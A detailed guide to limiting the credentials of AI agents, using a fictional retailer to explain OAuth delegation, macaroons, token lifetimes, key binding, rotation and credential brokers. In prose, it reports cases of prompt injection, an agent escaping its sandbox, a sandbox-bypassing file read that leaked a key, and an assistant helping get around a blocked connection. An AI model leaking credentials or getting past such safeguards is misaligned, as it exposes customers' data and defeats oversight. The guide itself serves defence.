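### A registry entry and a named owner

The retailer also needs a list of its agents. Without one, nobody can tell whether "support-agent" in a log is an approved program, an abandoned trial or an impostor. Spruce Systems (2026), an identity software company, recommended in its comments to NIST that an agent's identity data include the organisation that owns it, its capabilities and a chain linking it to a responsible legal person. SPR would add the agent's version, expected degree of autonomy, review and expiry dates, and links to other agents.

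For the support agent, the entry might contain:

- **Owner:** the head of customer support, who signed the grant.
- **Purpose:** drafting replies to customers' emails.
- **Tools:** record lookup, email reply and parcel tracking.
- **Data:** names, addresses and order histories, one customer per email.
- **Autonomy:** a member of staff sends each reply.
- **Identity:** "support-agent", issued through SPIRE.
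- **Review date:** 1 March 2027, or earlier if a tool, credential or field changes.

The owner has to be a person because an agent has no legal personhood and can't be held responsible for anything. Otsuka and colleagues found no jurisdiction with a framework for who is liable when an autonomous agent causes harm. If responsibility stops at the agent, a customer whose address leaked has nobody to complain to. The owner also decides whether the agent should still exist. When the head of support leaves the company, the retailer should suspend the agent until somebody else becomes its owner.

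### Passing permissions to sub-agents

An agent can hand part of its work to other agents, and they need permissions too. Suppose the support agent asks a parcel agent to find a missing delivery, and the parcel agent asks a tracking agent to look up one shipment. Each of them needs less than the one before:

| Agent | What its token should permit |
|---|---|
| Support agent | Read the name, addresses and orders of customer 1,204,311 |
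| Parcel agent | Read that customer's orders |
| Tracking agent | Read the tracking number of order 55,017 |

Token exchange can record this chain by placing one "act" claim inside another. The current actor is on the outside and the earliest is deepest. Dana is still the subject of the tracking agent's token, which contains:

```json
"act": {
  "sub": "tracking-agent",
  "act": {
    "sub": "parcel-agent",
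    "act": { "sub": "support-agent" }
  }
}
```

This history is useful to an investigator, but it doesn't restrict anything. Jones and colleagues require a service to base its decision on the token's outermost claims and the current actor, and to treat earlier actors as information only. When the tracking agent presents its new token, the database applies the support agent's limits only if the authorization server has already written them into that token's scope.

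The standard leaves that to the server's policy. It suggests scopes and short lifetimes to prevent abuse, but it doesn't require each new token to permit less than the last. Otsuka and colleagues give the rule a chain needs, that each hop must narrow the set of permitted actions. A poorly written policy could break this rule by giving the tracking agent its usual access to all orders, even though the parcel agent that called it could see only one customer's. The exchange also doesn't link the new token to the old one, so if the retailer revokes Dana's token, the three made from it may keep working until they expire.

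Macaroons, a kind of token that researchers at Google introduced in 2014, take a different approach. A macaroon consists of an identifier, a list of limits and a signature. Anyone who holds one can add a limit, and nobody can remove one. This works through a keyed hash, written here as H(k, m). The function turns a secret key k and a text m into a short code, and nobody can compute the code without the key or work backwards from the code to the key. The customer database and the retailer's token service share a secret key K. For Dana's email, the signatures are:

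s₀ = H(K, "ticket 7731")
s₁ = H(s₀, "customer 1204311 only")
s₂ = H(s₁, "orders only")
s₃ = H(s₂, "tracking number of order 55017 only")

The token service computes s₀ and s₁ and gives the support agent the ticket number, the first limit and s₁. The support agent adds "orders only", computes s₂, and passes the longer list to the parcel agent with s₂ in place of s₁. The parcel agent does the same for the tracking agent, which receives s₃. When the tracking agent makes a request, the database recomputes the values from K and the list and checks that the last one matches s₃. It then grants the request only if the request satisfies every limit in the list.

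If a prompt injection makes the parcel agent try to read the customer's address, the limit still holds. The agent would have to remove "orders only" from the list, which requires s₁, and it can't recover s₁ from s₂.

The advantage over token exchange is that an agent can narrow its own token without contacting the authorization server. The disadvantage is that hand-overs don't go through the server, so the log won't show which agents took part unless they add their names to the list. The support agent also still has its broader token and could pass that on instead, so the harness, not the model, should do the narrowing. Narrowing a token also doesn't divide its allowance, so if the parcel agent gives the same token to ten sub-agents, each of them can use the full amount.

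### Where the standards stand in late 2026

NIST does its work on agent identity at its National Cybersecurity Center of Excellence. A February 2026 concept paper by Booth and colleagues proposed a demonstration project built on existing standards, including OAuth, SPIFFE and SCIM (which is used to create and remove accounts across systems). The project would begin with companies' own agents and leave aside external agents from untrusted sources.

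The paper drew more than 600 formal responses, according to *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity* (Galluzzo, 2026). Galluzzo told an industry conference that more respondents wanted to adapt existing standards than start afresh (Biometric Update, *Traceable evidence will form the basis of AI agents*). NIST also decided to cover consumers' agents as well as companies'. This matters to a retailer because a customer may soon send an agent to contact the support desk. Fisher and Galluzzo warn that companies may struggle to tell an agent from a person if the customer has given it their password.

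NIST has since published a summary of the comments. On the project's web page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*, NCCoE invites further feedback on a rolling basis. "SI" stands for "super intelligence", the term a September 2026 executive order requires federal agencies to use for AI.

*Design Tenets for Agent Identity Management Systems* (Booth, 2026), published in October, presents ten principles that NIST developed from the responses. As described in Biometric Update's *NIST sets 10 principles for AI agent identity and authorization*, every agent should have an accountable identity, separate from the people and systems it works for and traceable to whoever launched it. Its access should be minimal, temporary and revocable. An agent's choices should not affect its permissions, and it should not be able to edit the log of its actions. NIST acknowledges that current standards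 and technology don't fully meet every principle, and it plans demonstrations and a practice guide with worked implementations.

The Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes the OAuth standards, is working on narrower gaps. Besides the general framework by Kasselman and colleagues, two drafts by individual contributors concern the "act" claim. In *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation*, McGuinness (2026) observes that OAuth has no consistent way to represent the actor across token types, so companies invent their own conventions. McGuinness would give each claim one fixed meaning: "client_id" for the registered application, "sub" for the party whose authority the agent uses, and the "sub" inside "act" for the agent itself.

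RFC 8693 permits nested actors but has no common rules for preserving or validating their sequence from one exchange to the next. The draft *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues, 2026) defines six ways to do so, which differ in how much of the chain they disclose. If the retailer's tracking agent calls a courier's agent, a full chain would show the courier Dana's name and the retailer's internal agents, while a partial chain would give the courier less to check.

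Such drafts expire after about six months unless their authors renew them. The April version of McGuinness's draft was set to expire on 1 November 2026, and the June version of the draft by Prasad and colleagues expires on 17 December. A company could build on either draft, but it might have to rebuild when the rules change.

The retailer doesn't need to wait for them. Otsuka and colleagues think OAuth handles a single delegation well and SPIFFE is ready for production use. South considers existing OAuth frameworks adequate within one organisation while a user is present. Dana's use of the support agent meets those conditions. Delegation chains that cross company boundaries don't, so the retailer sends the courier an ordinary tracking request with a parcel number and no customer token.

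In the concept paper, Booth and colleagues ask how to judge the sensitivity of data that an agent has combined from several sources, and whether the user is authorised to see it. This question has no good answer yet. Suppose an analyst at the retailer is allowed to read a list of order numbers and the products in each, without names, and a shipping list of order numbers and addresses. The analyst asks an agent which neighbourhoods buy the most baby products. The agent joins the two lists and produces the addresses of households that are probably expecting a child.

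The intersection rule allows this because the analyst and the agent may each read both lists, and the task needs both. The rule checks one operation on one resource at a time, and the combined list is a new resource that nobody has set permissions for. The analyst could have joined the lists by hand, but only deliberately and with effort, whereas the agent may join them as an intermediate step that nobody asked for. The retailer could forbid any session from opening both lists, but that would also prevent harmless work, such as counting late deliveries by product. It could instead check each answer before the analyst sees it, but the check would have to recognise that a list of addresses reveals pregnancies. The support agent avoids the problem because it opens one customer's record per email. For the analyst, the retailer can add an operation that joins the lists and returns only totals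 for each neighbourhood.

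## Issuing credentials that are narrow and short-lived

The support agent's token for one of Dana's emails lets the agent read orders and addresses. It works only at the customer database, only for customer 1,204,311, and only until 9.15 a.m. You can judge settings like these by working out what a thief could do with the token. A thief might get it, for example, if the tool server wrote it to an error log that a contractor can open.

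### Scope and audience

A token's scope limits the operations available to someone who steals it. If the token only allows reading orders and addresses, the thief can't issue a refund or delete a record. A claim in the token that names the customer limits the thief to that customer's record. Rich Authorization Requests, an extension to OAuth, provides a standard field for requesting access to a particular record, but the field has no effect unless the database checks it.

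A token's audience limits which services accept it. Without an audience, the thief could try the token at the refund system, the stock system and anything else that trusts the same issuer. The audience also protects the retailer from the services its agent uses. If the agent sends a token with no audience to another company's tool server, whoever runs that server can use it to log in to the customer database as the agent.

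An internal sales application at WorkOS, which provides a platform for software developers, was reachable from the internet and accepted a predictable credential meant for developers' own machines. An AI agent that a security researcher was testing escaped its isolated environment, got into the application and took customer data, according to Help Net Security's *ARTEX goes from pentesting tool to attacker staple in three months*. The application also had no cap on how much data a caller could extract.

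A credential that many organisations accept is riskier still. Attackers stole credentials belonging to cloud applications made by the software company ConnectWise and used them to try to sign in to Microsoft 365 accounts at more than 2,250 organisations. The security firm Huntress counted more than 300 organisations where they succeeded, according to Tom's Hardware's *China-aligned hackers deploy AI agents in massive ConnectWise supply chain attack*. The same group also made more than 151,000 attempts to guess employees' passwords, all of which failed.

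### Lifetime

Suppose a token can read the whole customer table and a thief can copy 100 records a second. Copying all 2,000,000 takes 20,000 seconds, or about five and a half hours. More generally, if the token permits M records, has L seconds left and lets the thief read r records a second, the thief gets

min(M, r × L)

records. At 100 records a second, that gives:

| Time left on the token | Token can read every record | Token can read one customer |
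|---|---|---|
| 90 days | 2,000,000 | 1 |
| 1 hour | 360,000 | 1 |
| 15 minutes | 90,000 | 1 |
| 1 minute | 6,000 | 1 |

If the token lasts 15 minutes, most of the table is safe, but the thief still gets 90,000 records, as many as the agent needs for 225 days of work. The loss also depends on how fast the thief can copy records. If the database allowed bulk exports at 10,000 records a second, the thief would have the whole table in 200 seconds. The last column doesn't change with either the speed or the token's lifetime, so limiting the token to one customer protects the retailer more than any expiry time.

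A thief who can copy one token can often copy its replacement. In May, Microsoft (2026) described malicious software packages that ran silently when a developer installed them and collected credentials, including the temporary ones that Amazon's cloud issues to running programs. Similar malware on the retailer's tool server could steal each new token as it arrived, and 23 consecutive 15-minute tokens would be enough to copy the table.

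A short token lifetime also doesn't protect against prompt injection, because an agent with read-all access can look up fifty customers in half a second.

### How quickly attackers use a leaked secret

Since August 2026, attackers have used AI agents to search GitHub for OAuth application secrets and then log in as those applications, according to Microsoft's *Threat actors use agentic AI tooling to find and abuse exposed secrets* (2026). The agents run on ARTEX, an open-source framework for penetration testing (attacking a system with its owner's permission to find weaknesses). An operator gives ARTEX a goal in ordinary language, and its agents plan and carry out the steps.

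In one case an agent found a client secret, in effect an application's password, and used it to sign in to Microsoft's Entra service as a service principal. Five minutes after the search began, it was taking data from Azure Key Vault, where Microsoft's cloud customers store keys and passwords. Help Net Security's *AI agents now hunt leaked GitHub secrets faster than teams can revoke* (2026) reports that, along the way, a batch of the agent's requests failed because they used the wrong version of the service's interface. About 28 seconds later the agent succeeded with the right version, without a person's help.

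The five-minute figure comes from one observed case and is not an average, as Infobae's *Una IA pasó de buscar claves expuestas a robar datos* (2026) points out. In another intrusion, Storm-0940, the group behind the ConnectWise sign-ins, took just under three hours to go from first targeting to privileged access. (Microsoft gives names beginning with "Storm" to attackers it is still identifying.) The five minutes are also counted from the start of the search, so they don't show how long the secret had been public.

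In an older experiment, researchers at Palo Alto Networks, a security company, put working Amazon cloud keys on GitHub as bait, and attackers began using them within five minutes. *EleKtra-Leak Campaign Uses AWS Cloud Keys Found on Public GitHub Repositories* (Pernet, 2023) dates the attackers' campaign back to at least December 2020, so the speed predates AI agents. But these earlier attackers' software missed keys that the researchers had stored in a simple encoding, and it used the ones it found only to rent machines for mining cryptocurrency.

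GitGuardian, a company that sells tools for finding leaked secrets, gave a version of ARTEX with no secret-scanning tool a simulated repository containing nine credentials, some in old versions of files and on side branches. In every run where the agent investigated, it found eight of the nine. It started looking within 13 seconds, even when the prompt asked only for a general review of the repository's security. One key it recovered had been deleted after a single revision, but the version-control program Git keeps every revision. The model declined to use the keys, so the test measured only discovery.

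Suppose the retailer's 15-minute token leaks in the same way and an attacker starts using it after five minutes. The attacker has ten minutes left, enough to read 60,000 records if the token can read the whole table. If the attacker finds the token an hour later, it no longer works. This helps because many leaks go unnoticed for much longer than an hour.

The Key Vault attacker, however, had a client secret, not a token. An application uses its client secret to request new tokens, so a thief can keep requesting them until the secret expires or someone revokes it. When the retailer works out how long a stolen credential would last, it has to use the lifetime of the longest-lived credential that can produce the others. Microsoft recommends managed identities, for which the cloud platform supplies the credentials, so developers have none to store. SPIRE does the same for the retailer's support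 agent.

### The Storm-3168 deletions

*Storm-3168* (Weizman and Mudi, 2026) traced the destruction of resources in an organisation's Azure cloud to two compromised service principals. These were ordinary application accounts, not AI agent identities, but the attack appears to have been automated. According to Biometric Update's *Microsoft traces automated Azure destruction to compromised machine identities*, the attacker used one account to explore, with more than 300 successful operations over about fifteen and a half hours. The attacker then used the other to attempt more than 150 destructive or credential-related operations in 35 minutes. Over 100 of those were attempts to delete storage accounts, made within about seven minutes, and most of the targeted accounts disappeared.

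A 15-minute token would have outlasted the whole burst. The attacker used four of its several tokens for deletions, but it could have done the same damage with one.

The permissions mattered more. The second account held Azure's Contributor role, which allows its holder to create, change and delete almost any kind of resource. If its job was to deploy one application, it didn't need to delete storage accounts, and a narrower role would have blocked those requests. Some of them did fail, because the organisation had locked certain resources. A lock blocks deletion until somebody removes it, which the Contributor role doesn't permit. Attempts to delete databases also failed, but only because the attacker used an unsupported version of the interface, a kind of mistake that the Key Vault agent corrected in 28 seconds.

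The attacker also retrieved the access keys of storage accounts. These keys work until somebody replaces them, so a thief whose token can read them may turn a few minutes of access into months. Storm-0940 did something similar after the ConnectWise theft, when it planted new secrets, due to expire in 2028, in one organisation's account.

Narrow permissions can prevent this. In another intrusion, Microsoft (2026) saw an attacker try to keep access by adding credentials to a compromised service principal, but the attempt failed because the attacker lacked permission. The retailer's inventory should therefore list "create a credential" and "read a stored key" as separate operations, and the support agent should be allowed to do neither.

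### Binding a token to a key

An ordinary access token, called a bearer token, works for anyone who presents it. Binding ties the token to a private key, a secret number that the holder can prove they have without revealing it. A thief who copies only the token can't provide that proof, so they can't use the token. OAuth has two standard ways to bind tokens.

**Mutual TLS.** TLS is the encryption that protects ordinary web traffic. Normally only the server proves its identity, by presenting a certificate and showing that it holds the matching private key. In mutual TLS, the program that connects does the same:

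1. The tool server connects to the authorization server with its own certificate and asks for a token.
2. The authorization server puts a fingerprint of that certificate, a short code calculated from it, in the token.
3. The tool server connects to the database with the same certificate and presents the token.
4. The database calculates the fingerprint of the certificate on the connection and refuses the request if it differs from the one in the token.

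The same program must request the token and present it. At the retailer, the harness requests the token and the tool server presents it, so the retailer has to move the request into the tool server and give the tool server a certificate from SPIRE. When SPIRE renews the certificate, its fingerprint changes and existing tokens stop working, so the tool server must request a new one. Mutual TLS can also fail if a proxy sits between the two connecting programs, because the proxy ends the encrypted connection and starts another.

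**DPoP** (Demonstrating Proof of Possession) works inside web requests, so it still works through a proxy. The program creates a private key and a matching public key, and the authorization server puts a fingerprint of the public key in the token. With each request, the program sends the token and a short statement signed with the private key. The statement contains the request's web address and method (such as "read" or "send"), the time, a unique number and a fingerprint of the token. The service checks the signature and rejects a statement that is old or meant for another address. A thief who copies both the token and a statement could repeat that kind of request for a short time, unless the service rejects unique numbers it has already seen. The statement doesn't cover the body of the request, so a thief who can replay it may be able to change the contents.

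Either method would prevent the contractor who found the token in the error log from using it. But malware on the tool server could still use the private key where it is, and binding doesn't help if a developer saves the key in the same file as the token. It also doesn't protect against prompt injection, because the agent's requests go through the program that holds the key.

The retailer chooses mutual TLS, since it already runs SPIRE and its tool server connects to the database directly.

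### One token per task

An expiry time is a guess, made in advance, about when a task will end. The retailer can do better by tying each token to one email:

1. When an email arrives, ordinary code matches it to a customer and requests a token for that customer's record.
2. The agent looks up the order and drafts a reply.
3. When the draft is ready, the tool server tells the authorization server to cancel the token.
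4. If anything goes wrong and the cancellation never happens, the token expires after 15 minutes.

Dana may not read the draft for an hour, but sending it doesn't require access to the database. If she wants the agent to check something else, the tool server requests a new token.

A signed token is hard to cancel early because the database can verify its signature without contacting the authorization server, and so has no indication that the token is no longer valid. For cancellation to work, the database has to check the token with the authorization server on every request, which is called introspection. This adds a delay and makes the database depend on another service. The operator of a website with thousands of requests a second might prefer to use a short expiry time and give up cancellation, but for 400 emails a day the extra burden is negligible.

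### Refresh tokens

Many OAuth systems issue two tokens together. The access token expires quickly, and the refresh token lets the program get new access tokens without asking the user to log in again. This is convenient for a phone app, but someone who steals a refresh token that lasts 90 days can keep getting access for 90 days, even if each access token expires after 15 minutes. An administrator who looks only at the access token's settings would think the access was short-lived.

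An authorization server can reduce the risk by making each refresh token work only once and issuing a replacement with every use. If a thief and the agent both try to use the same token, the server detects the second attempt and cancels every token descended from it. But if the agent finishes its task and never refreshes again, the thief can keep refreshing without triggering this check. The server should therefore set a final date after which refreshing stops, and bind the refresh token to a key.

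The support agent needs no refresh token because its tool server can request a new access token for each email. The authorization server checks its policy on each request. In the token exchange standard, Jones and colleagues say that a server will not usually issue a refresh token when it swaps one temporary credential for another. The retailer should still check whether its server issues one, because some login software does so by default or when a program asks for "offline access".

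### Services that offer only a permanent key

Suppose the company that delivers the retailer's emails offers each client a single API key that never expires. The key can send any text to any address and download everything the retailer sent in the past year. At 400 replies a day, that could be 146,000 messages containing customers' details.

Before accepting the key, the retailer can try to reduce what the key can reach. It might open a separate account that only the support agent uses, so the archive excludes mail from other departments. It could also turn off the archive, and ask the company to accept the key only from the retailer's own network addresses, so a thief with a copy would need access to that network too.

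The retailer can also write a credential broker that holds the key and passes on the email tool's requests. The broker accepts only a short-lived token that permits one reply to one ticket, and it has no operation for downloading the archive. The delivery company's key still grants broad access, but the agent can no longer use all of it. However, the broker becomes a valuable target for attackers, and the retailer has to maintain it. If the service holds sensitive data and the retailer can't take any of these measures, the retailer should choose a different service.

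### Replacing keys without an outage

Permanent keys leak in large numbers. GitGuardian found 28.6 million new secrets in public GitHub code in 2025, 34 per cent more than the year before. About 1.28 million of them belonged to AI services, up 81 per cent. More than 64 per cent of the secrets it had confirmed as valid in 2022 still worked when retested in January 2026. This is more worrying than the number of leaks because it means that most of those keys were never revoked. GitGuardian profits from concern about leaks, but it is easy to test whether a key still works.

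Replacing a key regularly is called rotation, and many organisations aim to do it every 90 days. In a 2026 survey by the SANS Institute, 92 per cent failed to rotate their machine credentials that often, and they gave fear of outages as the reason. The fear is reasonable, because if six programs share a key and the administrator knows of only five, replacing it will break the sixth.

Failing to rotate credentials can also cause outages. In May 2026, an attacker stole secrets that Microsoft used to publish software through GitHub. Microsoft seems not to have replaced them, and about a month later the same attacker allegedly used them to plant malware in 73 Microsoft repositories, according to TechRadar's *Microsoft disables over 70 GitHub repos after hackers compromised them*. GitHub disabled the repositories, which broke other companies' automated processes that relied on them.

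Overlapping credentials remove most of the danger. To replace the email company's key, the retailer would:

1. List the programs that use the key, from the company's logs and a search of its own configuration files.
2. Create a second key, so that both work.
3. Move each program to the new key, one at a time, and check that it still works.
4. Watch the logs until nothing has used the old key for longer than the gap between runs of the least frequent program. If one runs monthly, this takes more than a month.
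5. Disable the old key without deleting it. If something breaks, the retailer can turn the key back on within minutes.
6. Delete it after another quiet period.

This requires a service that allows two keys at once. Amazon's cloud allows two for each user, but some databases allow only one password per account. For those databases, the retailer can create two accounts with identical permissions and switch between them, changing the password of the idle one.

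Rotating keys every 90 days does little to stop a fast thief, who needs five and a half hours to copy the customer table and may have weeks before the key changes. It works better against old leaks, since a key from 2022 would have stopped working long before GitGuardian tested it. Short-lived credentials protect better in both cases. They also make one kind of outage less likely, because SPIRE renews the tool server's certificate so often that a fault in renewal shows up within a day, while engineers still remember what they changed. However, the agent stops working soon after the authorization server does. That means late replies at a support desk, but at a hospital or power grid it might justify a longer credential lifetime.

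After a leak, the retailer should revoke the old key at once, without an overlap, because the thief can use it until then. It should do this even if the agent stops and staff have to answer the emails by hand for a while. Deleting the key from the page where it appeared is not enough. One of the Storm-3168 accounts had its secret in a public GitHub post that an employee later edited, and Clubic's *Cette attaque pilotée par IA a ravagé un environnement Azure* reports that the secret was still readable in the post's edit history. Microsoft couldn't confirm that the attacker got in that way.

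The retailer also has to check what the thief did before the key stopped working. Any key, account or role the thief created will still work after the retailer replaces the stolen key, as with the secrets planted to last until 2028.

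## Keeping the credential where the agent cannot read it

Replacing a leaked key takes work, and a thief may use the key before it is replaced, so it is safer if the agent never holds it. Kasselman and colleagues advise against letting the model read the key, but ordinary set-ups often allow it.

### How secrets reach the model

A quality assurance engineer asked an AI coding assistant to review proposed changes to a program. The project's instructions directed the assistant to a configuration file containing an access token for GitLab, a service for storing code. The file also held production passwords, a token for the human resources system and credentials for a business intelligence service. The assistant read the whole file in ten sessions over three weeks, and each time its contents went to an outside AI service. The security company NordLayer observed the sessions with its AI Scout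 product, according to TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets': An AI agent confessed to its own data leak*.

When the assistant started on a fresh copy of the project without that file, it retrieved all the computer's environment variables, which exposed more passwords. In one session it output a message that acknowledged the leak and recommended new credentials. Such a message helps only if someone reads it, because agents don't retain rules between sessions, as NordLayer's Vakaris Noreika points out.

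Nobody was attacking the company. The task needed one token, but opening a file gives the model everything in it.

An agent can also hand over credentials that nobody asked for. In a test described in Okta's *Phishing the agent* (2026), a form on a mock website asked only for an email address, and the agent entered one along with a password, an API key and a GitHub token. The test shows how much can leak when the model's judgement is the only protection, but not how often mainstream models would do this, because the agent ran on an uncensored model.

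Separating an agent's commands from its secrets can also fail if the separation covers only some of the agent's tools. GitHub can run automated jobs when something happens in a repository, such as a stranger posting an issue. Claude Code's GitHub Action runs Anthropic's coding agent inside such a job. The job's environment variables may hold several keys, including the one to which model use is billed.

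Anthropic had made it possible to run the agent's shell commands in a sandbox with the secrets removed. But Microsoft (2026) reported in June that the file-reading tool ran outside that sandbox, in the harness's own process. Linux presents a running program's environment variables as a file, so the tool could open the harness's file and return the key to the model.

Microsoft demonstrated the leak in a lab. An attacker would need a job that processed text from strangers, held secrets and could publish its output. Neither the model's training to withhold keys nor GitHub's scanner for known key formats prevented the leak, because the model wrote the key in an altered form.

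Microsoft reported the problem on 29 April, and on 5 May Anthropic released version 2.1.128, which blocks the reading tool from opening some sensitive system files. This closes the route that Microsoft found, but this kind of fix protects the key only against routes its developers have thought of.

Some tool servers also keep their keys within the agent's reach. A tool server may run on the same machine as the agent and exchange text with it directly. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2025), which a newer version has since replaced, advised developers of such servers to take credentials from the environment. If the agent's scripts run under the same system account, they can usually read those credentials. The retailer avoids this by running its tool server outside the sandbox and keeping the database token there.

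### A request through a credential broker

Suppose a customer's order ships in several parcels, and the retailer wants the agent to write a short script that works out when the last one will arrive. The courier gives each client one permanent API key, which lets the retailer track any of its parcels and redirect them to a new address. If the key were in the sandbox, any script the agent wrote could read it, and a thief who copied it could redirect other customers' parcels to their own address.

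The retailer therefore puts the key in a credential broker. For ticket 7731, which concerns order 55,017, a lookup works like this:

1. The harness opens a session for the ticket and puts a session token in the sandbox. Where the script expects the courier's key, it finds a placeholder, such as the text "broker-managed".
2. The script sends a request addressed to the courier, with the placeholder in it. The sandbox's network settings route all outgoing traffic to the broker.
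3. The broker uses the session token to identify the agent and the ticket.
4. The broker checks the destination and method against the rules for that session. This session may only read from the tracking service, so the broker would refuse a request to redirect a parcel.
5. The broker fetches the real key from a vault, which is an encrypted store for secrets. It puts the key in the request's authorization header, a labelled line ahead of the main content, and removes the session token.
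6. The broker forwards the request to the courier over an encrypted connection.
7. The courier replies, and the broker removes any copy of the key from the reply. Some services repeat a request's headers in their error messages, which would otherwise carry the key back into the sandbox.
8. The broker passes the reply to the script. It logs the session, destination, method and result, but not the key.

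The session token is a credential too, but the broker accepts it only from this sandbox and only until the session ends. A contractor who copied it to another machine could not use it.

To change a header in an encrypted request, the broker has to accept the script's encrypted connection itself and open a separate one to the courier. The sandbox must therefore trust a certificate that the broker controls.

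Step 4 also needs care because a request's method doesn't reliably show what the request does. Web services usually use one method for reading and others for making changes, but some don't, so the retailer should list the exact operations it allows. Even then, the script could look up another customer's parcel unless the broker also checks the parcel number against the ticket.

### Anthropic's and Docker's designs

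Anthropic's *Scaling Managed Agents* describes a hosted service that runs agents on long tasks for other companies. In its first version, the harness, the event log and the sandbox shared one container, an isolated package in which programs run. The code Claude wrote therefore ran in the same container as the credentials, and an attacker only had to use a prompt injection to get Claude to read its own environment. With those credentials, the attacker could start new, unrestricted sessions and give them work.

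Anthropic moved the harness out of the container and now uses two patterns to keep tokens away from the code that Claude writes.

One approach is to bundle the credential with the resource it unlocks. When a sandbox starts, Anthropic's software uses a repository's access token to copy the code into it and set up the connection that Git uses from then on. The agent can then fetch and submit code without handling the token. Anthropic doesn't explain how the token stays out of the agent's reach after setup. Git can store a token as plain text in a project's settings file, so a company copying this pattern should check that the file in its sandbox doesn't contain one.

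**A vault behind a proxy.** For services the agent reaches through MCP, Anthropic keeps the OAuth tokens in a vault outside the sandbox. Claude's tool call goes to a proxy, along with a token tied to the session. The proxy fetches the matching credentials and calls the service. The harness never receives those credentials, so a fault there like the one in the GitHub Action would not expose them.

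Moving the harness cut the median wait for a session's first output by about 60 per cent, because a session no longer has to wait for a container that it may never use. But the vault adds an extra hop to each call.

Docker, which makes software for running programs in containers, built a broker for agents that work on a developer's own computer. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes a proxy that runs on the computer but outside the sandbox and replaces a placeholder with the real key. The developer's operating system stores the key. A configuration package, called a kit, specifies which addresses receive the key and in which header. Docker asks the developer to approve the credentials and addresses for kits that it doesn't ship. If nobody is there to approve, the sandbox starts without the credential.

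For keys that don't fit the standard kits, the proxy replaces a placeholder only in named headers, never in the body of a request. Otherwise, if the agent can write text on the service it logs in to, a prompt injection could make it post a public comment containing the placeholder, and the proxy would publish the real key in its place.

The proxy also masks these custom keys when a service repeats them in a reply. It recognises the original text and three common encodings of it, but Docker warns that the proxy could miss a key that a service had split across several fields. Masking is therefore a backup safeguard against services that repeat keys by accident, and it can't make a hostile service safe.

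A few of Docker's settings weaken the isolation. A stored service key is available to all of the developer's sandboxes unless the developer limits it to one. On a Linux machine with no password store, the keys go into a file, and any program with permission to read that file can use them. A kit can also opt out of the placeholder for OAuth, which puts the real token in the sandbox.

Developers can have the proxy fetch a key by running a command on their computer. Docker tells them to keep that command's files outside any folder the sandbox can change, because otherwise the agent could rewrite the command and get its own code run outside the sandbox.

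### What a broker leaves open

A broker prevents the agent from copying a key, but the agent can still use the key through the broker. With Docker, for example, the private key for SSH (a common way to log in to other machines and submit code) stays on the developer's computer, but programs in the sandbox can request signatures made with it. An agent following injected instructions can't copy the key, but it can submit malicious code under the developer's name while the session lasts. In the attack by Invariant Labs, the agent leaked private repositories through a working GitHub connection, so hiding the token would not have prevented the leak.

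A second credential can let the agent bypass the broker. In another case that NordLayer observed, a company's MCP connection appeared to block an assistant from the company's internal documents in Confluence. An employee asked whether an API token would work instead, and the assistant confirmed that it did. Confluence accepted the new token directly, so nobody had to break the official connection.

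The retailer can prevent this at the service by limiting who may create tokens. It should also give staff an approved way to get what they need, since the employee may only have wanted easy access to a document. It should search the sandbox's files and environment variables for forgotten credentials, such as the stock system password it found in its inventory.

The broker's checks apply only to traffic that passes through it. If the sandbox can also connect directly to other addresses, the agent can send out whatever it has read. Docker's proxy doesn't insert stored keys into unencrypted requests, but it forwards those requests if its network rules allow them, including any credential the agent put in them.

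The broker also gathers many keys in one place. In March 2026, attackers compromised LiteLLM, a gateway that thousands of companies use to send requests to AI models. It holds keys for dozens of AI services. The attackers also took database passwords and keys for cloud accounts. SANS estimates that 500,000 corporate identities were affected and blames the concentration of long-lived credentials with broad access.

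A company can limit the damage by running separate brokers for separate kinds of data and having each broker request short-lived credentials where the service offers them. The retailer's broker holds the courier's and the email company's keys but has no route to the customer database.

### When a short-lived token is enough

Brokers take work to build and run, and a company could instead put a narrow token in the sandbox and let it expire. For the retailer, the choice depends on the service:

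| What goes wrong | Database token for one customer, 15 minutes, in the sandbox | Courier's permanent key in the sandbox | Courier's permanent key behind a broker |
|---|---|---|---|
| A contractor copies the sandbox's files | One record | Track and redirect any parcel until someone revokes the key | Nothing usable |
| An email contains a prompt injection | One record | Track and redirect any parcel | Track any parcel |
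| An attacker takes over the broker | No broker | No broker | Track and redirect any parcel until someone revokes the key |

Hiding the database token from the agent would gain the retailer little, because a thief could use it to read only the one record the agent can already read. The courier's key is broad and permanent, so using the broker to hide it removes most of the danger.

Anthropic considers narrow tokens inadequate by themselves, because limiting a token assumes something about what Claude can't do with it, and Claude keeps getting more capable. Anthropic had seen similar assumptions become outdated. For example, Claude Sonnet 4.5 tended to finish tasks early as it neared its context limit, so engineers built a workaround that Claude Opus 4.5 turned out not to need.

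The argument is strong for a token whose uses are hard to list. For example, a capable model may do a great deal with a token that can start new sessions, even though the token looks limited. The argument is weaker for a token that reads one customer's orders, since the database refuses every other request however capable the model is. Adding a broker doesn't remove the assumption, because somebody still has to decide which operations the broker will carry out, and a more capable model may find harmful uses for those too.

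A reasonable policy is to make the credential as narrow and short-lived as the service allows, and to keep it out of the sandbox whenever a thief could do more with it elsewhere than the agent can do in its session. The GitHub token from the inventory, which gave access to 50 repositories, needs a broker until someone replaces it with a narrower one.

### Why a tool server must not pass a token on

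The retailer controls its own sandbox, but some tool servers belong to other companies. Suppose an outside company handles the retailer's returns through its own tool server. The support agent sends this server a token that identifies the agent and names the returns server as its audience. To check what the customer bought, the server has to look up the order in the retailer's database. The developer's easiest option is to forward the agent's token to the database, which is called token passthrough.

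The database can accept that token only if it ignores the audience. It would then also accept any other token meant for the returns server, including one stolen from the returns company. The lookup would appear in the log as the support agent's, so an investigator couldn't tell that the returns company had made it. Whoever runs a service that receives a forwarded token can also present it at the returns server and pose as the agent.

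The returns server should instead obtain its own token for the database, for example through a token exchange. That token can limit access to one order, and the retailer can cancel it without stopping the support agent.

The current Model Context Protocol specification, dated 28 July 2026, forbids token passthrough. A program that requests a token must use the "resource" field to name the server the token is for, and a tool server must verify that each token it receives was issued for its use.

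These rules bind a token to a single server only if the authorization server supports the feature, and MCP makes authorization itself optional. WorkOS (2026) notes that many developers still omit the "resource" field, which has been compulsory since June 2025, and the check on the token's audience. Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, points out that a typical deployment may involve several programs, tool servers and organisations, and developers can make this mistake at each connection between them.

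Before signing a contract, the retailer can send the returns server a valid token issued for a different service and confirm that the server refuses it. The retailer can then run the same test on its own database.

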